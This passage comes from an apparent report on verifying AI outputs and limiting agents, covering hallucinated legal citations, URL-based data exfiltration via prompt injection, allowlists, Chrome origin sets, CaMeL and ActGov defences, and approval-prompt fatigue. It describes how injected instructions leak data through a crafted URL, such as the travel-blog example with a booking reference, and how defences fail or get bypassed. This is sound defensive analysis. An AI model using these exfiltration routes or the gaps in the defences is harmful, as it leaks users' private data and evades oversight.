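| The name and number belong to different cases | A lookup | Over 80% |
| The cited page is wrong | The opinion with its official page numbers | 52.8% |
| The quotation has altered words | The opinion | 95.2% |
| The brief misstates the ruling | The opinion and a judgement about its meaning | 83.2% |

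Overall, GPT-5 caught 84.4% of the errors, but only 40.8% of the passages it flagged were among the known errors. Claude Code with Opus 4.8 caught fewer errors (62.8%), but 76.1% of its flags were correct. About a quarter of the citations in the full dataset contained an error. That share is probably far lower in ordinary filings, so a court would see a higher proportion of false alarms.

A few of the agent's apparent false alarms were real citation errors. It found more than ten that lawyers had made before language models were common, such as `216 F.3d 659` for `276 F.3d 659`.

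Other false alarms came from gaps in CourtListener, the free database. The test included 132 correct citations that a CourtListener lookup couldn't find. Gemini 2.5 Flash flagged 65.9% of them as hallucinated, while GPT-5 flagged 25.0% and confirmed 40 of the rest by searching elsewhere. Missing page numbers also caused problems, because for many cases only Westlaw and LexisNexis have them. People who represent themselves in court often can't afford those services.

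CanLII, a free Canadian database, has nearly complete coverage of decisions since 2001, so a Canadian tribunal could reasonably expect people to check that a case exists. But Liu, Stammbach and Henderson note in *Can AI reduce burdens on courts by automatically verifying citations?* that CanLII didn't allow automated agents.

Most citation checking in US courts is still manual. According to Bloomberg Government's *AI-Faked Cases Become Core Issue Irritating Overworked Judges*, opposing lawyers often find false citations, and judges find some themselves. The judge can then order the lawyer who filed them to explain them, and can also impose a penalty.

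Courts also have to decide which citations count as fabricated. The Volokh Conspiracy's *Court Finds AI Hallucinations in Filing by Former State Senate Candidate* (2026) reproduces a New York ruling that fined a lawyer $2,500. The court counted a citation as fabricated only if nobody could find the case by name, or if the case wasn't where the lawyer said and had nothing to do with the claim. It excluded apparent typing errors, correct citations with the wrong case name, and real cases on the right topic whose rulings the lawyer had completely misstated.

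Checking that a cited case exists is a fair way to decide whether somebody made it up, but it misses a very common error, which is citing a real authority for something it doesn't support. *Commit or Abstain?* (Demir, 2026) cites a public tracker with 2,203 court matters involving AI hallucinations, 1,264 of them from 2026. This error occurred in 933 of the 2,203 matters, or 42%.

The rules make whoever files the document mainly responsible for checking it. Demir reports that California's state bar has proposed requiring lawyers to verify that the authorities they cite exist and are accurate. Texas has proposed requiring anyone who signs a filing to state that its citations, quotations and descriptions of rulings aren't fabricated.

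Others want software to check filings before a judge reads them. Liu and colleagues suggest automated screening at or before filing, with court clerks helping people fix any problems it finds. Walter (2026), in *Why AI Disclosure Rules Do Not Stop Hallucinated Citations and What Could*, proposes that lawyers submit the cited cases along with the brief. This would give the checker the text it needs, but the court would still have to confirm that the copies are genuine.

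Law firms can already buy something similar. Above the Law's *New Tool Catches AI Hallucinations in Legal Briefs* (2026) describes RealityCheck, which first checks case names, volumes and courts against legal databases without using AI. A model then helps with the rest of the analysis. This order makes sense because a lookup takes little compute and doesn't depend on a model's output.

### What a model adds as judge

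Code can search a source for an exact quotation, but it can't reliably check whether a paraphrase has the same meaning. A model can match "deaths fell by half" to a table in which mortality drops from 8% to 4%. It can also detect when a writer has changed "may help some patients" to "helps patients".

A judge that can read the source can do much better than the models that Yuan and colleagues asked to verify skill names from memory. The judge in *Verified Misguidance* had the page's text and reached a balanced accuracy of 91.8% on fidelity.

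It can still raise false alarms. GPT-5 wrote that about 99.4% of people infected with Covid-19 in the United States did not die, and cited an official page. The page estimated 146.6 million infections and 921,000 deaths. The judge labelled the citation fabricated because the page didn't contain the figure 99.4%. But the calculation is simple:

1 − 921,000 / 146,600,000 ≈ 99.4%

The page therefore supports the number, but not GPT-5's added remark that death alone is too narrow a standard. A better judge would assess the two claims separately, or at least require a calculation before rejecting the number.

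Different judging methods can also give different results for the same answers. Das and colleagues report a broad error rate, which counts unsupported and contradicted claims, and a strict one, which counts only contradictions. The strict rate should therefore never be higher, but for the GPT-5 system with the fewest errors on the civil code, the broad rate was 8.3% of answers and the strict rate was 16.6%. The most likely explanation is that the two rates come from different judging methods, which produced different labels for the same claims.

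### Errors that the judge shares with the writer

A judge model may repeat the writer model's mistake if both learned the same false claim in training. Both may also miss a qualification for the same reason, for example because the software gave them only one paragraph of a long paper. A second model doesn't help much in that case because it also lacks the missing text.

A judge may also accept the closest match when nothing fits, as models do with lists of permitted values. Demir gave ten models passages from court opinions and asked which holding, meaning the point of law a court decided, belonged with the case each passage cited. In 1,670 of 5,314 items, Demir replaced the right holding with a similar one from another case, so the correct choice was "none of these". Six ordinary language models picked a holding in 38% to 86% of those items. In one example that Demir prints, all six, which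 came from five different companies, chose the same wrong holding, so a majority vote among them would have kept the error and made it look more certain.

(The test measures whether models can choose a holding from its context. They didn't read the cited cases, which would give a judge more to work with.)

Demir also tested four decision models, which return a probability for each option instead of writing text. The most cautious of them, Jev, picked a wrong holding in 30% of the items that had no correct holding. But it chose "none of these" for 26.2% of the items that did have one, compared with under 8% for every ordinary model. Accepting the best ordinary model's answer only when a decision model agreed halved that model's wrong citations. Disagreements go to a person, so the benefit depends on how many of them a firm can review.

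Asking a model to review its own work, or another model's, can fail badly if nobody opens the source. Greenberg Traurig's *From Hallucination To Sanctions* (2026) describes a New York lawyer who put a brief through three rounds of AI review without personally checking the citations. Fourteen of the 60 cases in the brief didn't exist. After more false citations in later filings, the judge entered a default judgment against the lawyer's client in February 2026, and in October ordered the lawyer to pay nearly $39,000 in fees and costs.

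In another case, a law clerk found fabricated quotations in a draft that a lawyer had written with Claude. According to The Straits Times' *Courts cracking down on error-strewn AI-assisted legal briefs* (2026), the lawyer asked Claude to correct them and filed the result without reading it. The judge then found seven quotations that were either missing from the original decisions or misrepresented.

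Requiring a judge model to copy out the sentence it relied on could make its verdict easier to trust. Code can then confirm that the sentence appears in the source, and a person can compare it with the claim in a few seconds. The model also needs a "can't tell" option for papers behind a paywall and court opinions with missing pages. Quotations can be checked without a judge model, since an exact text search would have caught every quotation of the lawyer's that didn't appear in the decision he cited.

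## Limiting which addresses an agent may open

To check a citation, software has to open the cited page, which sends the page's full address to the website. Websites commonly log these addresses, so whoever runs the site can read any private data the addresses contain.

Suppose an employee of Norvane, the made-up logistics company, asks an assistant to plan a business trip. The assistant can read the employee's email, which includes a booking reference, `KX41T9`. It also reads a travel blog with hidden instructions in the text, and under their influence it requests this address:

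`https://travel-blog.example/map?ref=KX41T9`

The part after the question mark passes extra information to the site. The blog's owner now has the booking reference, even if the page is empty and the assistant never mentions the reference in its reply. The employee may not notice, because software can send such a request in the background when it loads an image or previews a link. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) calls this URL-based data exfiltration.

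A security researcher reported URL-based data exfiltration to OpenAI and Microsoft in 2023, according to the researcher's Embrace The Red blog post, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. Microsoft responded that May with a content security policy that generally stopped Bing Chat from loading images. OpenAI added its first check in December 2023, but initially left it out of its macOS and iOS apps.

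Filtering out hidden instructions before an agent reads them is unreliable. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces a 2025 attack that looks like a routine office email about a restructuring and worked in 50% of tests. OpenAI says filters don't usually catch attacks this well developed, because recognising one is as hard as recognising a lie. It therefore also tries to limit what a deceived agent can do, for example by restricting which addresses the agent can open.

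### A list of permitted domains

Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, shows how a domain allowlist works for an agent's network access. In the cloud version, a setup script with full internet access first installs the packages that the project needs. The agent then starts work, offline by default. OpenAI makes passwords and other configured secrets available during setup but removes them before the agent starts.

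A developer who wants the agent online can turn access on for a particular project environment. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* describes three starting points:

| Setting | What the agent can reach |
|---|---|
| None | Only domains that the developer adds |
| Common dependencies | A preset list of sites for downloading and building software, plus any that the developer adds |
| All | Every domain |

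The developer can also limit the agent's web requests to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, which normally retrieve information instead of uploading it.

In OpenAI's own example of an attack, a developer asks Codex to fix a reported bug, and the report contains a command that sends the project's latest commit message to an outside server. Either restriction would block the command, because the server isn't on the preset list and the command uses POST, a type of request that uploads data.

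Neither restricting the request type nor using the preset list is fully secure. A GET request still carries an address, so restricting the request type wouldn't have protected the booking reference. Willison (2025) warns in *Codex agent internet access* that any of the 71 domains on the preset list might offer a way to leak data. Some, such as GitHub, host material from the public. The list also includes PyPI and npm, so it doesn't stop an agent from installing a package whose name a model invented.

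OpenAI is stricter with its own staff's use of Codex. *Running Codex safely* describes a network policy that permits expected destinations, blocks certain others and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. Web search uses only OpenAI's cached copies of pages, so the agent can read a page without contacting the site.

### Redirects and too many warnings

OpenAI argues that a list of trusted sites helps but isn't enough for a general assistant. One reason is that a website can redirect a request to a different address, as many legitimate sites do. If the software checks only the first domain, a link can start on a trusted site and end on an attacker's.

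This is mostly an argument against carelessly written allowlists. Software that checks every address in the chain would stop at the first one that isn't permitted.

OpenAI's other objection, that a strict list produces frequent false alarms, is harder to address. People visit far more sites than any list of well-known ones contains, and frequent warnings can train them to click through without thinking. The objection is weaker for a coding agent that needs a few dozen sites than for an assistant that plans trips, shops and answers medical questions.

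### An index of addresses that are already public

OpenAI's alternative is to check whether the exact address is already public. An address that existed on the open web before the conversation, and independently of it, is much less likely to contain the user's private data. The check works like this:

1. A crawler, a program that explores the web by following links, records the public addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
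2. When an agent is about to open an address automatically, software looks for that exact address in the crawler's index.
3. If it finds a match, the agent opens the page.
4. If it doesn't, the software either tells the agent to try a different site or shows the user a warning and lets them decide.

The Norvane employee's trip could produce all three outcomes:

| Address | In the index? | Result |
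|---|---|---|
| `hotel.example/contact`, a page that the hotel's home page links to | Yes | The agent opens it |
| `travel-blog.example/map?ref=KX41T9` | No | The software tells the agent to try another site |
| `files.example/share/7Qm2`, an itinerary that a colleague shared privately | No | The employee sees a warning and chooses to open it |

(OpenAI doesn't explain how the software chooses between the last two outcomes.)

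The address has to match an entry in the index exactly. The blog's plain map page, `travel-blog.example/map`, may well be in the index, but the version with the booking reference isn't, so the software doesn't have to identify which parts of an address are private. It also matters that the crawler doesn't learn addresses from users' conversations, because an address containing private data could then end up in the index.

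The index will lack some harmless pages, such as the shared itinerary, pages published a few minutes ago, and pages that a site creates for one visitor, so some warnings will be needless. As Embrace The Red understands it, ChatGPT reduces these warnings by treating an address that the user types as safe for the rest of that conversation.

OpenAI warns the user that the link isn't verified and may include information from the conversation. In March 2026, OpenAI said the system, which it calls Safe Url, shows the user the information that the agent would send. That should be easier to judge than a long address. The check covers page visits and bookmarks in OpenAI's Atlas browser, and searches and page visits in its Deep Research tool.

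OpenAI says the check is meant to stop an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address itself, but that it doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions, or that the site won't try to manipulate the user. A fake shop that the crawler has visited would pass, so confirming that a site is genuine requires a separate check.

Small leaks also remain possible. Even if every address an agent opens is public, its choice of one page over another can reveal something to whoever runs the site. Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges this, and suggests storing pages for a few minutes or refusing repeat visits to the same address within a session. The post also warns that some of OpenAI's developers may not know about the check and may leave it out of new features. Even so, it calls the system a significant improvement.

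### Sites that Chrome's agent may read or use

An agent inside a browser can cause more damage, because the user may already be logged in to a bank, an email account and an employer's systems. Browsers normally keep these separate with the same-origin policy, which stops a page on one site from reading a page on another. An origin is roughly a site's full domain plus the protocol and port the browser uses to reach it. An agent that reads several sites and types into them can carry information from one to another.

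In December 2025, Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, described Google's plan to restore the boundary. For each task, Chrome keeps two sets of origins. The agent may read content from the first and may also click and type on the second. If the user asks it to buy the ingredients for a recipe, the sets might work out like this:

| Origin | May the agent read it? | May the agent click and type? |
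|---|---|---|
| The recipe site | Yes | No |
| The grocery shop | Yes | Yes |
| An advertiser's frame inside the recipe page | No | No |
| The user's bank, open in another tab | No | No |

(A frame is a part of a page that another site can supply.)

The planning model, which reads web pages, can propose a new origin but can't add it. A separate gating function checks whether the origin is relevant to the task. This function never receives untrusted page content, so hidden text in the recipe can't influence it directly. If that text causes the planning model to propose the bank's site, the gating function should reject it because a bank has nothing to do with buying ingredients.

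The sets limit leaks but don't rule them out, because data can still pass from any site the agent may read to any site where it may type. Much like OpenAI, Chrome also restricts addresses that the model generates to known public ones. It asks the user before the agent opens certain sensitive sites, such as those for banking or medical information.

The first release tracked only the origins where the agent may click and type, and omitted the planned separate limit on what it may read. In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) tested seven browsers with built-in agents in January and February 2026. When they asked Chrome's agent about a page, its answers included text from a frame from a different origin, as did those of Claude for Chrome, Perplexity's Comet and Atlas in its agent mode.

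Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out a full data theft between test sites only in Atlas. The simple hidden instructions they tried didn't work on Chrome, but they didn't try to find sophisticated ones. They point out that Google hasn't made clear how it decides which origins are relevant or how well that decision withstands malicious input.

Google doesn't appear to have announced the missing reading limit since then. On August 4, 2026, Berschadski (2026) wrote in *Future Mode Part 2* that Google was "extending" Chrome's protections by limiting agents to relevant origins, but gave no release date for the reading limit. In the published code of Chromium (2025), the open-source project behind Chrome, asking the user before the agent opens a sensitive site is on by default, while confirming each new origin is off. The code also has a setting that hides other sites' frames in screenshots, but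 it belongs to a screenshot feature that is off by default. In a trial mode, the browser asks a server to assess a new origin and only records the answer. Google can change such settings remotely, so users may not get these defaults.

Companies can add their own list. Google's *Gemini in Chrome* names policies that let administrators specify the addresses where the agent may or may not act.

### Checking where an address came from

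The checks so far depend on the destination. A provenance check instead allows an action only if its arguments (the values the agent supplies, such as an address or a recipient) came from permitted sources. For example, a rule might forbid putting anything from the employee's inbox into a web address. This rule would stop the booking reference from leaking to trusted sites as well as unknown ones. A provenance check could also allow the colleague's private link if the employee had pasted it into their request to the agent.

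The best-known design is CaMeL, short for Capabilities for Machine Learning, which Google DeepMind published in 2025. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, welcomed it after two and a half years of "alarmingly little progress". It builds on Willison's own earlier idea of using two models, one that plans and one that reads. Suppose the employee asks the assistant to send Priya a summary of Tuesday's meeting notes. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends the design, describes steps like these:

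1. The planning model sees the employee's request but not the notes. It writes a short program:

```
notes = read_file("Tuesday meeting")
summary = reading_model("Summarise this", notes)
send_email("priya@norvane.example", summary)
```

2. Ordinary software, called an interpreter, runs the program line by line and makes the tool calls.
3. The reading model processes the notes and returns a summary. It can't call any tools.
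4. The interpreter labels every value with its origin. Here, the recipient came from the employee and the summary came from the notes.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the labels against the developer's policies.

Hidden instructions in the notes could distort the summary, but they couldn't add a fourth line to the program. The labels deal with a different danger. If the employee had written "send it to whoever chaired the meeting", the recipient would come from the notes, and an attacker who had edited them could choose the address. A policy that blocks recipients taken from documents would prevent this, but it would also block reasonable requests when the notes are genuine.

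*ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, September 2026) aims to keep the check while letting the agent change its plan as it reads. The agent proposes one action at a time, and ActGov intercepts each proposal. It turns the proposal and its context into a small set of facts with fixed possible values, such as whether the task permits this tool, whether the destination is trusted and where an argument came from. Code then applies the policies to those facts.

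A model drafts the policies in advance from descriptions of the tools, examples of ordinary tasks and records of failed defences. A program called a solver searches for any combination of facts that would satisfy the policies but break a stated safety rule. If it finds one, the policies go back for revision. In the main tests, GPT-5.5 drafted the policies over ten rounds and people reviewed the result.

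### Tasks completed and attacks stopped

Zhang and colleagues tested ActGov and CaMeL on two benchmarks. AgentDojo has office, banking, travel and messaging tasks with attacks hidden in the emails and pages that the agent reads. AgentDyn has more open-ended tasks, in which the agent often has to find out from those emails and pages what to do next. With DeepSeek-v4-pro as the agent, the results were:

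| | AgentDojo: ordinary tasks completed | AgentDojo: attacks that succeeded | AgentDyn: ordinary tasks completed | AgentDyn: attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 87.8% | 6.1% | 76.7% | 8.6% |
| ActGov | 75.5% | 0.0% | 60.0% | 0.7% |
| CaMeL | 20.4% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

The other three models gave similar results. CaMeL let through at most 0.2% of attacks, but an agent that does nothing would score just as well on security, and CaMeL completed no AgentDyn tasks with any model.

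ActGov's low attack rates overstate its benefit, because most attacks failed even without a defence. On AgentDyn, it prevented about eight successful attacks per 100 attempts, but agents completed about 17 fewer ordinary tasks per 100. That could be worthwhile for an agent that makes bank transfers but not for one that only tidies a calendar. Both benchmarks are older than ActGov, so nobody designed their attacks to get past it.

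CaMeL completes far fewer ordinary tasks than its reputation suggests. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) credits it with stopping nearly all AgentDojo attacks while keeping task performance comparable. But in the test reported in *SecureClaw* (2026), which introduces a rival defence, CaMeL stopped all 629 attacks and completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks, compared with 59 for SecureClaw.

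Part of the gap may come from how rivals adapted CaMeL to their own test software. Some of it comes from the policies, since Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) found in *The LLMbda Calculus* that turning them on halved CaMeL's task completion on AgentDojo's banking tasks. A result without policies can therefore look far better. CaMeL also fixes its plan before reading anything, which is a handicap when the instructions are in an email. Other kinds of defence also do worse on AgentDyn. In tests by *AgentDyn* (2026), Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist injected instructions, completed about 80% of AgentDojo tasks under attack but only 53.4% on AgentDyn.

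ActGov has trouble with unfamiliar tasks. When Zhang and colleagues used policies developed on AgentDojo for AgentDyn's tasks, no attacks succeeded, but the agent completed only 10.0% of ordinary tasks. With policies developed on AgentDyn, it completed 22.4% of AgentDojo's. A company that adds a new tool is therefore likely to see many wrong refusals until somebody updates the policies. When models wrote the policies without human review and with only half the training examples, the agent completed between 28.3% and 53.3% of AgentDyn tasks, depending on the model.

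### Losing track of where data came from

A provenance rule depends on correct labels for where each value came from. CaMeL's interpreter attaches these labels in code as it moves each value. ActGov has a model choose an argument's source from a fixed set of answers. ActGov then applies an exact rule to that label, but a wrong label can make the rule allow a bad action or block a good one.

Labels in code can also miss leaks. Garby and colleagues show that a program can reveal a secret without copying it. If an agent sends a message only when an account balance is below a certain amount, anyone who can see whether the message was sent learns something about the balance. CaMeL catches the simplest leaks of this kind, but Garby and colleagues describe others that it misses, including some in the software around the interpreter. They built an agent whose interpreter has machine-checked proofs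 about how labels spread. Their agent completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did without policies, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

Labels can also disappear when one agent passes work to another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system in which a coordinating agent gave jobs to specialised ones, each protected by CaMeL. The coordinator treated text from a database as untrusted but included it in a message to a second agent, which treated the whole message as its user's instructions. An attacker's text from the database could therefore change the second agent's plan.

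Such failures were rare in their benchmark, where attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL and 0.2% of the time when each agent had its own CaMeL. When Peters-Gill and colleagues sent instructions and untrusted data between agents through separate channels, so that the receiving agent's planning model never read the data, no attacks succeeded. This version completed fewer tasks, though the loss was modest for the strongest models.

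## What the checks cost the people who use them

Stricter controls on agents stop more attacks but leave more ordinary tasks unfinished. Checks on packages, links and citations have a similar drawback, because they also flag good items and somebody has to deal with every alarm.

### How many alarms are right

Suppose a checker examines 1,000 package names from a coding assistant's replies, and 4% of them are invented, which is close to the rates Churilov measured. Suppose also, for illustration, that the checker flags 99% of the invented names and 5% of the real ones. On average, it will catch 39.6 of the 40 invented names and wrongly flag 48 of the 960 real ones, so only about 45% of its alarms will be right.

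The general formula uses the share of items that are bad (*p*), the detection rate (*d*) and the false-alarm rate (*f*):

share of alarms that are right = *pd* / (*pd* + (1 − *p*)*f*)

The result drops quickly as bad items become rarer. With *d* still at 99%:

| Share of names that are bad | Alarms that are right, if *f* = 5% | Alarms that are right, if *f* = 0.5% |
|---|---|---|
| 4% | 45% | 89% |
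| 1% | 17% | 67% |
| 0.1% | 2% | 17% |

If a model invents fewer names, the same checker's alarms become less reliable. Catching more of the bad names barely helps. In the middle row, increasing *d* from 99% to 100% raises the first result from 16.7% to 16.8%, while cutting false alarms by 90% raises it to 67%.

A registry lookup can have a false-alarm rate below 5%. Churilov's earlier checker flagged 1,394 of roughly 30,000 package mentions by Claude Haiku 4.5, and the later recheck confirmed 1,098 of them. About 79% of the flags were correct, which implies a false-alarm rate of about 1%.

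False alarms also add up within a reply. With a 5% false alarm rate, a reply that names ten real packages has about a 40% chance of at least one false alarm, if the errors are independent. The checks can also remove good items without warning, so users can't question the removal. For example, voting between models discards some real skills, and a source list leaves out some useful pages.

### How people respond to approval prompts

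False alarms waste time and can teach people to ignore the next alarm. Some of the best evidence comes from coding agents, which ask for approval before they run many commands. Users of Claude Code approve 97% of these prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* earlier put the figure at 93%. Most commands are harmless, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people have stopped reading. But users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents for approval. They may read a plan more closely than a command, though a plan also gives them more to disagree with.

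Anthropic measured attention directly in 1,053 paid testers. Partway through each session, one prompt showed a clearly dangerous command, which never ran. 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automated reviewer blocked 89% of the same commands. Anthropic published these results while making that reviewer the default, so it had an interest in the comparison. None of the testers' own files were at risk, which may have made them less careful than usual.

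Programmers describe themselves as more attentive than that. Salerno, Gao and colleagues surveyed software practitioners who use agents in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026). Of the 107 who answered questions about permissions, 47.7% said they read requests carefully and 20.6% said they approve by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. But 76.6% said they look harder at requests to write, delete or gain extra privileges, so their attention may not have fallen equally for every kind of request.

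A similar change shows up in how people review code that agents submit to public projects. In *Habituation at the Gate*, Yu, Jia and colleagues (2026) followed 400 repeat reviewers over about seven months. The overall approval rate rose from 30.1% in the first half of each person's reviews to 36.8% in the second. Reviewers also left 22% fewer comments on specific lines in their last tenth of reviews than in their first. Approval of code written by people fell in the same projects, so reviewers had not become more lenient with everyone. The agents may have improved, which would justify some of the extra approvals. Yu and colleagues had no direct measure of code quality, but they think the drop in comments points more towards habit.

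Some approval prompts are also impossible to judge. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files and found that user review played a part in 105. In 80 of those, the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31, the prompt showed a command without its effect on the files. A request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code that file contains. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in real products likewise show a raw command on a single line.

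### Fewer prompts and their effect on safety

A sandbox can reduce permission prompts by giving an agent a restricted area where it can work without asking. Anthropic reports that sandboxing cut these prompts by 84% in its internal use. A second model can then review actions that would reach outside the sandbox.

*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes how OpenAI uses a model, instead of the user, to review Codex actions that would leave the sandbox. In an example based on internal use, 9,280 of 10,000 actions stayed inside the sandbox. The other 720 would each have interrupted the user under manual approval. The reviewing model allowed 713 and refused seven. Codex found a safer way to continue after four of the refusals and stopped to ask the user after three.

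Anthropic accepted more missed dangerous actions from its two-stage reviewer in exchange for fewer interruptions. The quick first stage blocked 8.5% of harmless actions and missed 6.6% of dangerous ones. Adding a slower second stage cut wrongful blocks to 0.4% but raised misses to 17%. The miss rates come from only 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond its instructions. If, hypothetically, one action in 1,000 were dangerous, about 1% of the actions blocked by the first stage alone would be dangerous, compared with 17% of those blocked by the two stages together.

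Anthropic's evidence suggests that safety improved. Among sessions that its monitoring had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% of those with automated review. A model graded the harm, and Anthropic didn't assign users to a mode, so the two groups may have been doing different work. Anthropic also paid an outside firm, Trajectory Labs, to try prompt injections. None of 720 attempts succeeded against its latest models with automated review. This is weak evidence that the reviewer helped, because only 0.09% succeeded when the same models ran with no permission checks.

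Fewer prompts can also reduce safety. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) asked 113 people from outside the software industry to supervise an assistant through a simulated day. Seven of the assistant's 18 actions went beyond the user's request, such as reading private messages or buying a $25 airport lounge pass. One group was asked to approve each action. People in another group first set their own rules for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each.

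The rules reduced prompts from 18.0 to 10.9 per person, but the share of unrequested actions that were blocked fell from 59.6% to 39.6%. People had set 114 of the 140 rules to "ask", which postponed most decisions, and then approved most of the assistant's requests. They felt about as much in control as the other group. Yan recruited some participants only for the rules group, so assignment wasn't fully random.

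Sending more decisions to people isn't always safer either. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) models a reviewer who tires with each request, and finds that a guard can let more harm through by referring more actions to that reviewer. The result comes from a model, not from observing people, but it is consistent with the drop from 17% to 5% among Anthropic's testers.

### How often people open the sources

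Citations let readers check an answer, but most readers don't use them. *Investigating Click Behaviors On Google Search Result Pages* (2026) found that only 1% of visits to Google result pages with an AI summary led to a click on a source cited in the summary. In a user study of several chatbots, *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References* (2026) found that people checked references most often with ChatGPT, where they hovered over about 22% of references and clicked about 12%. Most users were still satisfied with the answers.

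Rates are higher in some experiments. In *Breaking News Out of the Filter Bubble* (2026), people who searched for news with AI answers went straight to a cited article after 14.3% of searches, though they may have wanted the full article whether or not they doubted the summary. In *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Responses* (2025), 83 of 197 participants (42.1%) checked at least one citation during the whole experiment. That figure counts people, while Google's 1% counts page visits, so comparing them overstates the difference in behaviour.

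People's accounts of their own checking are harder to interpret. *When Should I Trust This?* (Warren, Eser and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 1,000 American chatbot users. Only 39 said they never verify answers, and 14 said they always do. In a British survey by Ipsos for a publishers' trade body, 26% of ChatGPT users said they would click at least one media link in a response. *Unreliable AI answers are 'good enough' for most users of platforms* (Reeves, 2026) adds that about a third of users don't feel the need to click if they completely trust the source. A respected publisher's name can therefore discourage readers from checking whether the answer matches the article. Skipping that check is risky, because 30.6% of citations failed the fidelity test in *Verified Misguidance*.

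### Labels and "verified" marks

Warren and colleagues, most of whom worked at Meta during the research, also ran an experiment with 5,151 people. Each person saw a screenshot of a chatbot answering a question about a house plant, a physics problem or the dose of a blood-pressure drug. Some answers were wrong, including one that gave a starting dose five times too high. The screenshots showed a confidence rating, source icons, both or neither.

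On a scale from 1 to 5, people rated the accuracy of correct answers at 3.78 on average and wrong answers at 3.63. Answers labeled high confidence averaged 3.77, and those labeled low confidence averaged 3.62. The confidence level shown affected ratings about as much as correctness did, and neither had much effect. No type of label reliably changed perceived accuracy compared with no label. Participants saw source icons in a picture and had no links to open, so the experiment doesn't show how sources affect people who read them.

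When people open a citation, its content affects how much they trust the answer. In *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Responses*, some answers carried random citations. Once people had checked those citations, they trusted the answers no more than answers without citations.

A mark suggesting that an answer has already been checked may have more influence. One of Warren and colleagues' interviewees took "very confident" to mean that the chatbot had verified its answer, and concluded, "So I wouldn't need to do that." In *UXer-AI Collaboration Process for Enhancing Trust* (2025), a small study of designers, some participants trusted a tool more just because it offered ways to verify its output.

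*Verified, not generated* (2026) studied university course materials that a model had written and an expert had checked. Students relied on the "expert-verified" label instead of checking the materials systematically themselves, which was reasonable because they knew the expert from their tutorials. But the label can stay on the materials after the expert starts checking hastily, for example because the amount of material has grown faster than the time the expert has to check it.

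An automatic checker's mark can be wrong from the start. In *Fact-Check Your Information (FYI)* (2026), a small study of data-based articles, an automatic checker recognised misleading claims in only 12 of 29 cases and marked most of the others "verified". The participants did slightly better, recognising them in 15 of 29.

### Whether a visible check makes people less careful

If an assistant puts a tick beside a package because it exists, a programmer might stop wondering who maintains it. The closest evidence comes from labels on images. *That's another doom I haven't thought about* (2025) found that labelling AI-generated images made people more likely to believe misleading claims that appeared with unlabelled images. They seem to have taken a missing label as a sign that the claim was true, although the labels were only about the images' origin. An earlier study of headlines, which the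 paper cites, found no such effect.

Yan's results support the same conclusion. People who had set their own rules approved 66.8% of the unrequested actions they saw, compared with 40.3% among people who reviewed every action individually. Part of the gap could arise because the rules had already blocked some of the most objectionable actions, but even counting those, about 60% of the unrequested actions went ahead in the rules group. Having set rules may have made people feel protected, though Yan didn't test that explanation.

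The claim is plausible, but the evidence is indirect. A proper test would show programmers the same packages with and without a tick confirming that the package exists, then count how many check who maintains it. In the meantime, a developer can limit the risk with a narrower message. "This name is on PyPI; nobody has reviewed the code" is accurate and less reassuring than "verified". When people do the checking, *Verified, not generated* recommends recording what they checked, who did it and when.

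### Delay, upkeep and exceptions

In Yan's study, people spent an average of 142 seconds on 18 approvals, or about eight seconds each, so 100 prompts would take 13 minutes. The interruptions are probably a bigger burden than the time spent answering, because an agent that needs approval every few minutes can't work through the night or while its user is in a meeting. Automated review avoids most of that delay but uses extra computing for each action it examines.

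Teams also have to maintain their sandboxes and their lists of approved packages and sites. Anthropic describes sandboxes as safe but demanding, since each new capability needs configuring. If a team puts this off, ordinary work keeps triggering reviews. In that case, OpenAI advises Codex users to correct the sandbox's limits instead of teaching the reviewer to keep approving the same harmless requests.

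When a boundary gets in the way, people make their own exceptions, which tend to be broad. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule allowing some shell commands to run without a permission prompt. Many of these rules allowed any Python command, which is nearly the same as allowing everything. A quarter of interactive sessions began with permission checks switched off. Trębacz and colleagues found similar Python rules at OpenAI, and one settings file that always allowed Codex to start another copy of itself in its unrestricted "yolo" mode.

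An exception does less damage if it covers one exact command and expires. According to OpenAI, Codex lets a user approve an action once or approve that type of action for the current session, so neither choice becomes permanent by accident. A company also needs a quick way to request a lasting exception, because a programmer with a deadline will look for a way around the check if approval takes a week.

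People who work around the checks may turn to a tool the company hasn't approved. An employer can find an overly broad rule in a settings file, but it may never learn that someone has pasted a question into a personal chatbot account, where none of its checks apply. The figures from Anthropic and OpenAI cover only workarounds inside their own products, so they don't show how often people use outside tools this way.

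### Blocking, warning, asking or replacing

Once a check flags an item, the software can respond in four ways:

| Response | If the item was good | If the item was bad | Suits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Block | The user or agent has to find another way | It does no harm | Irreversible actions with a large possible loss |
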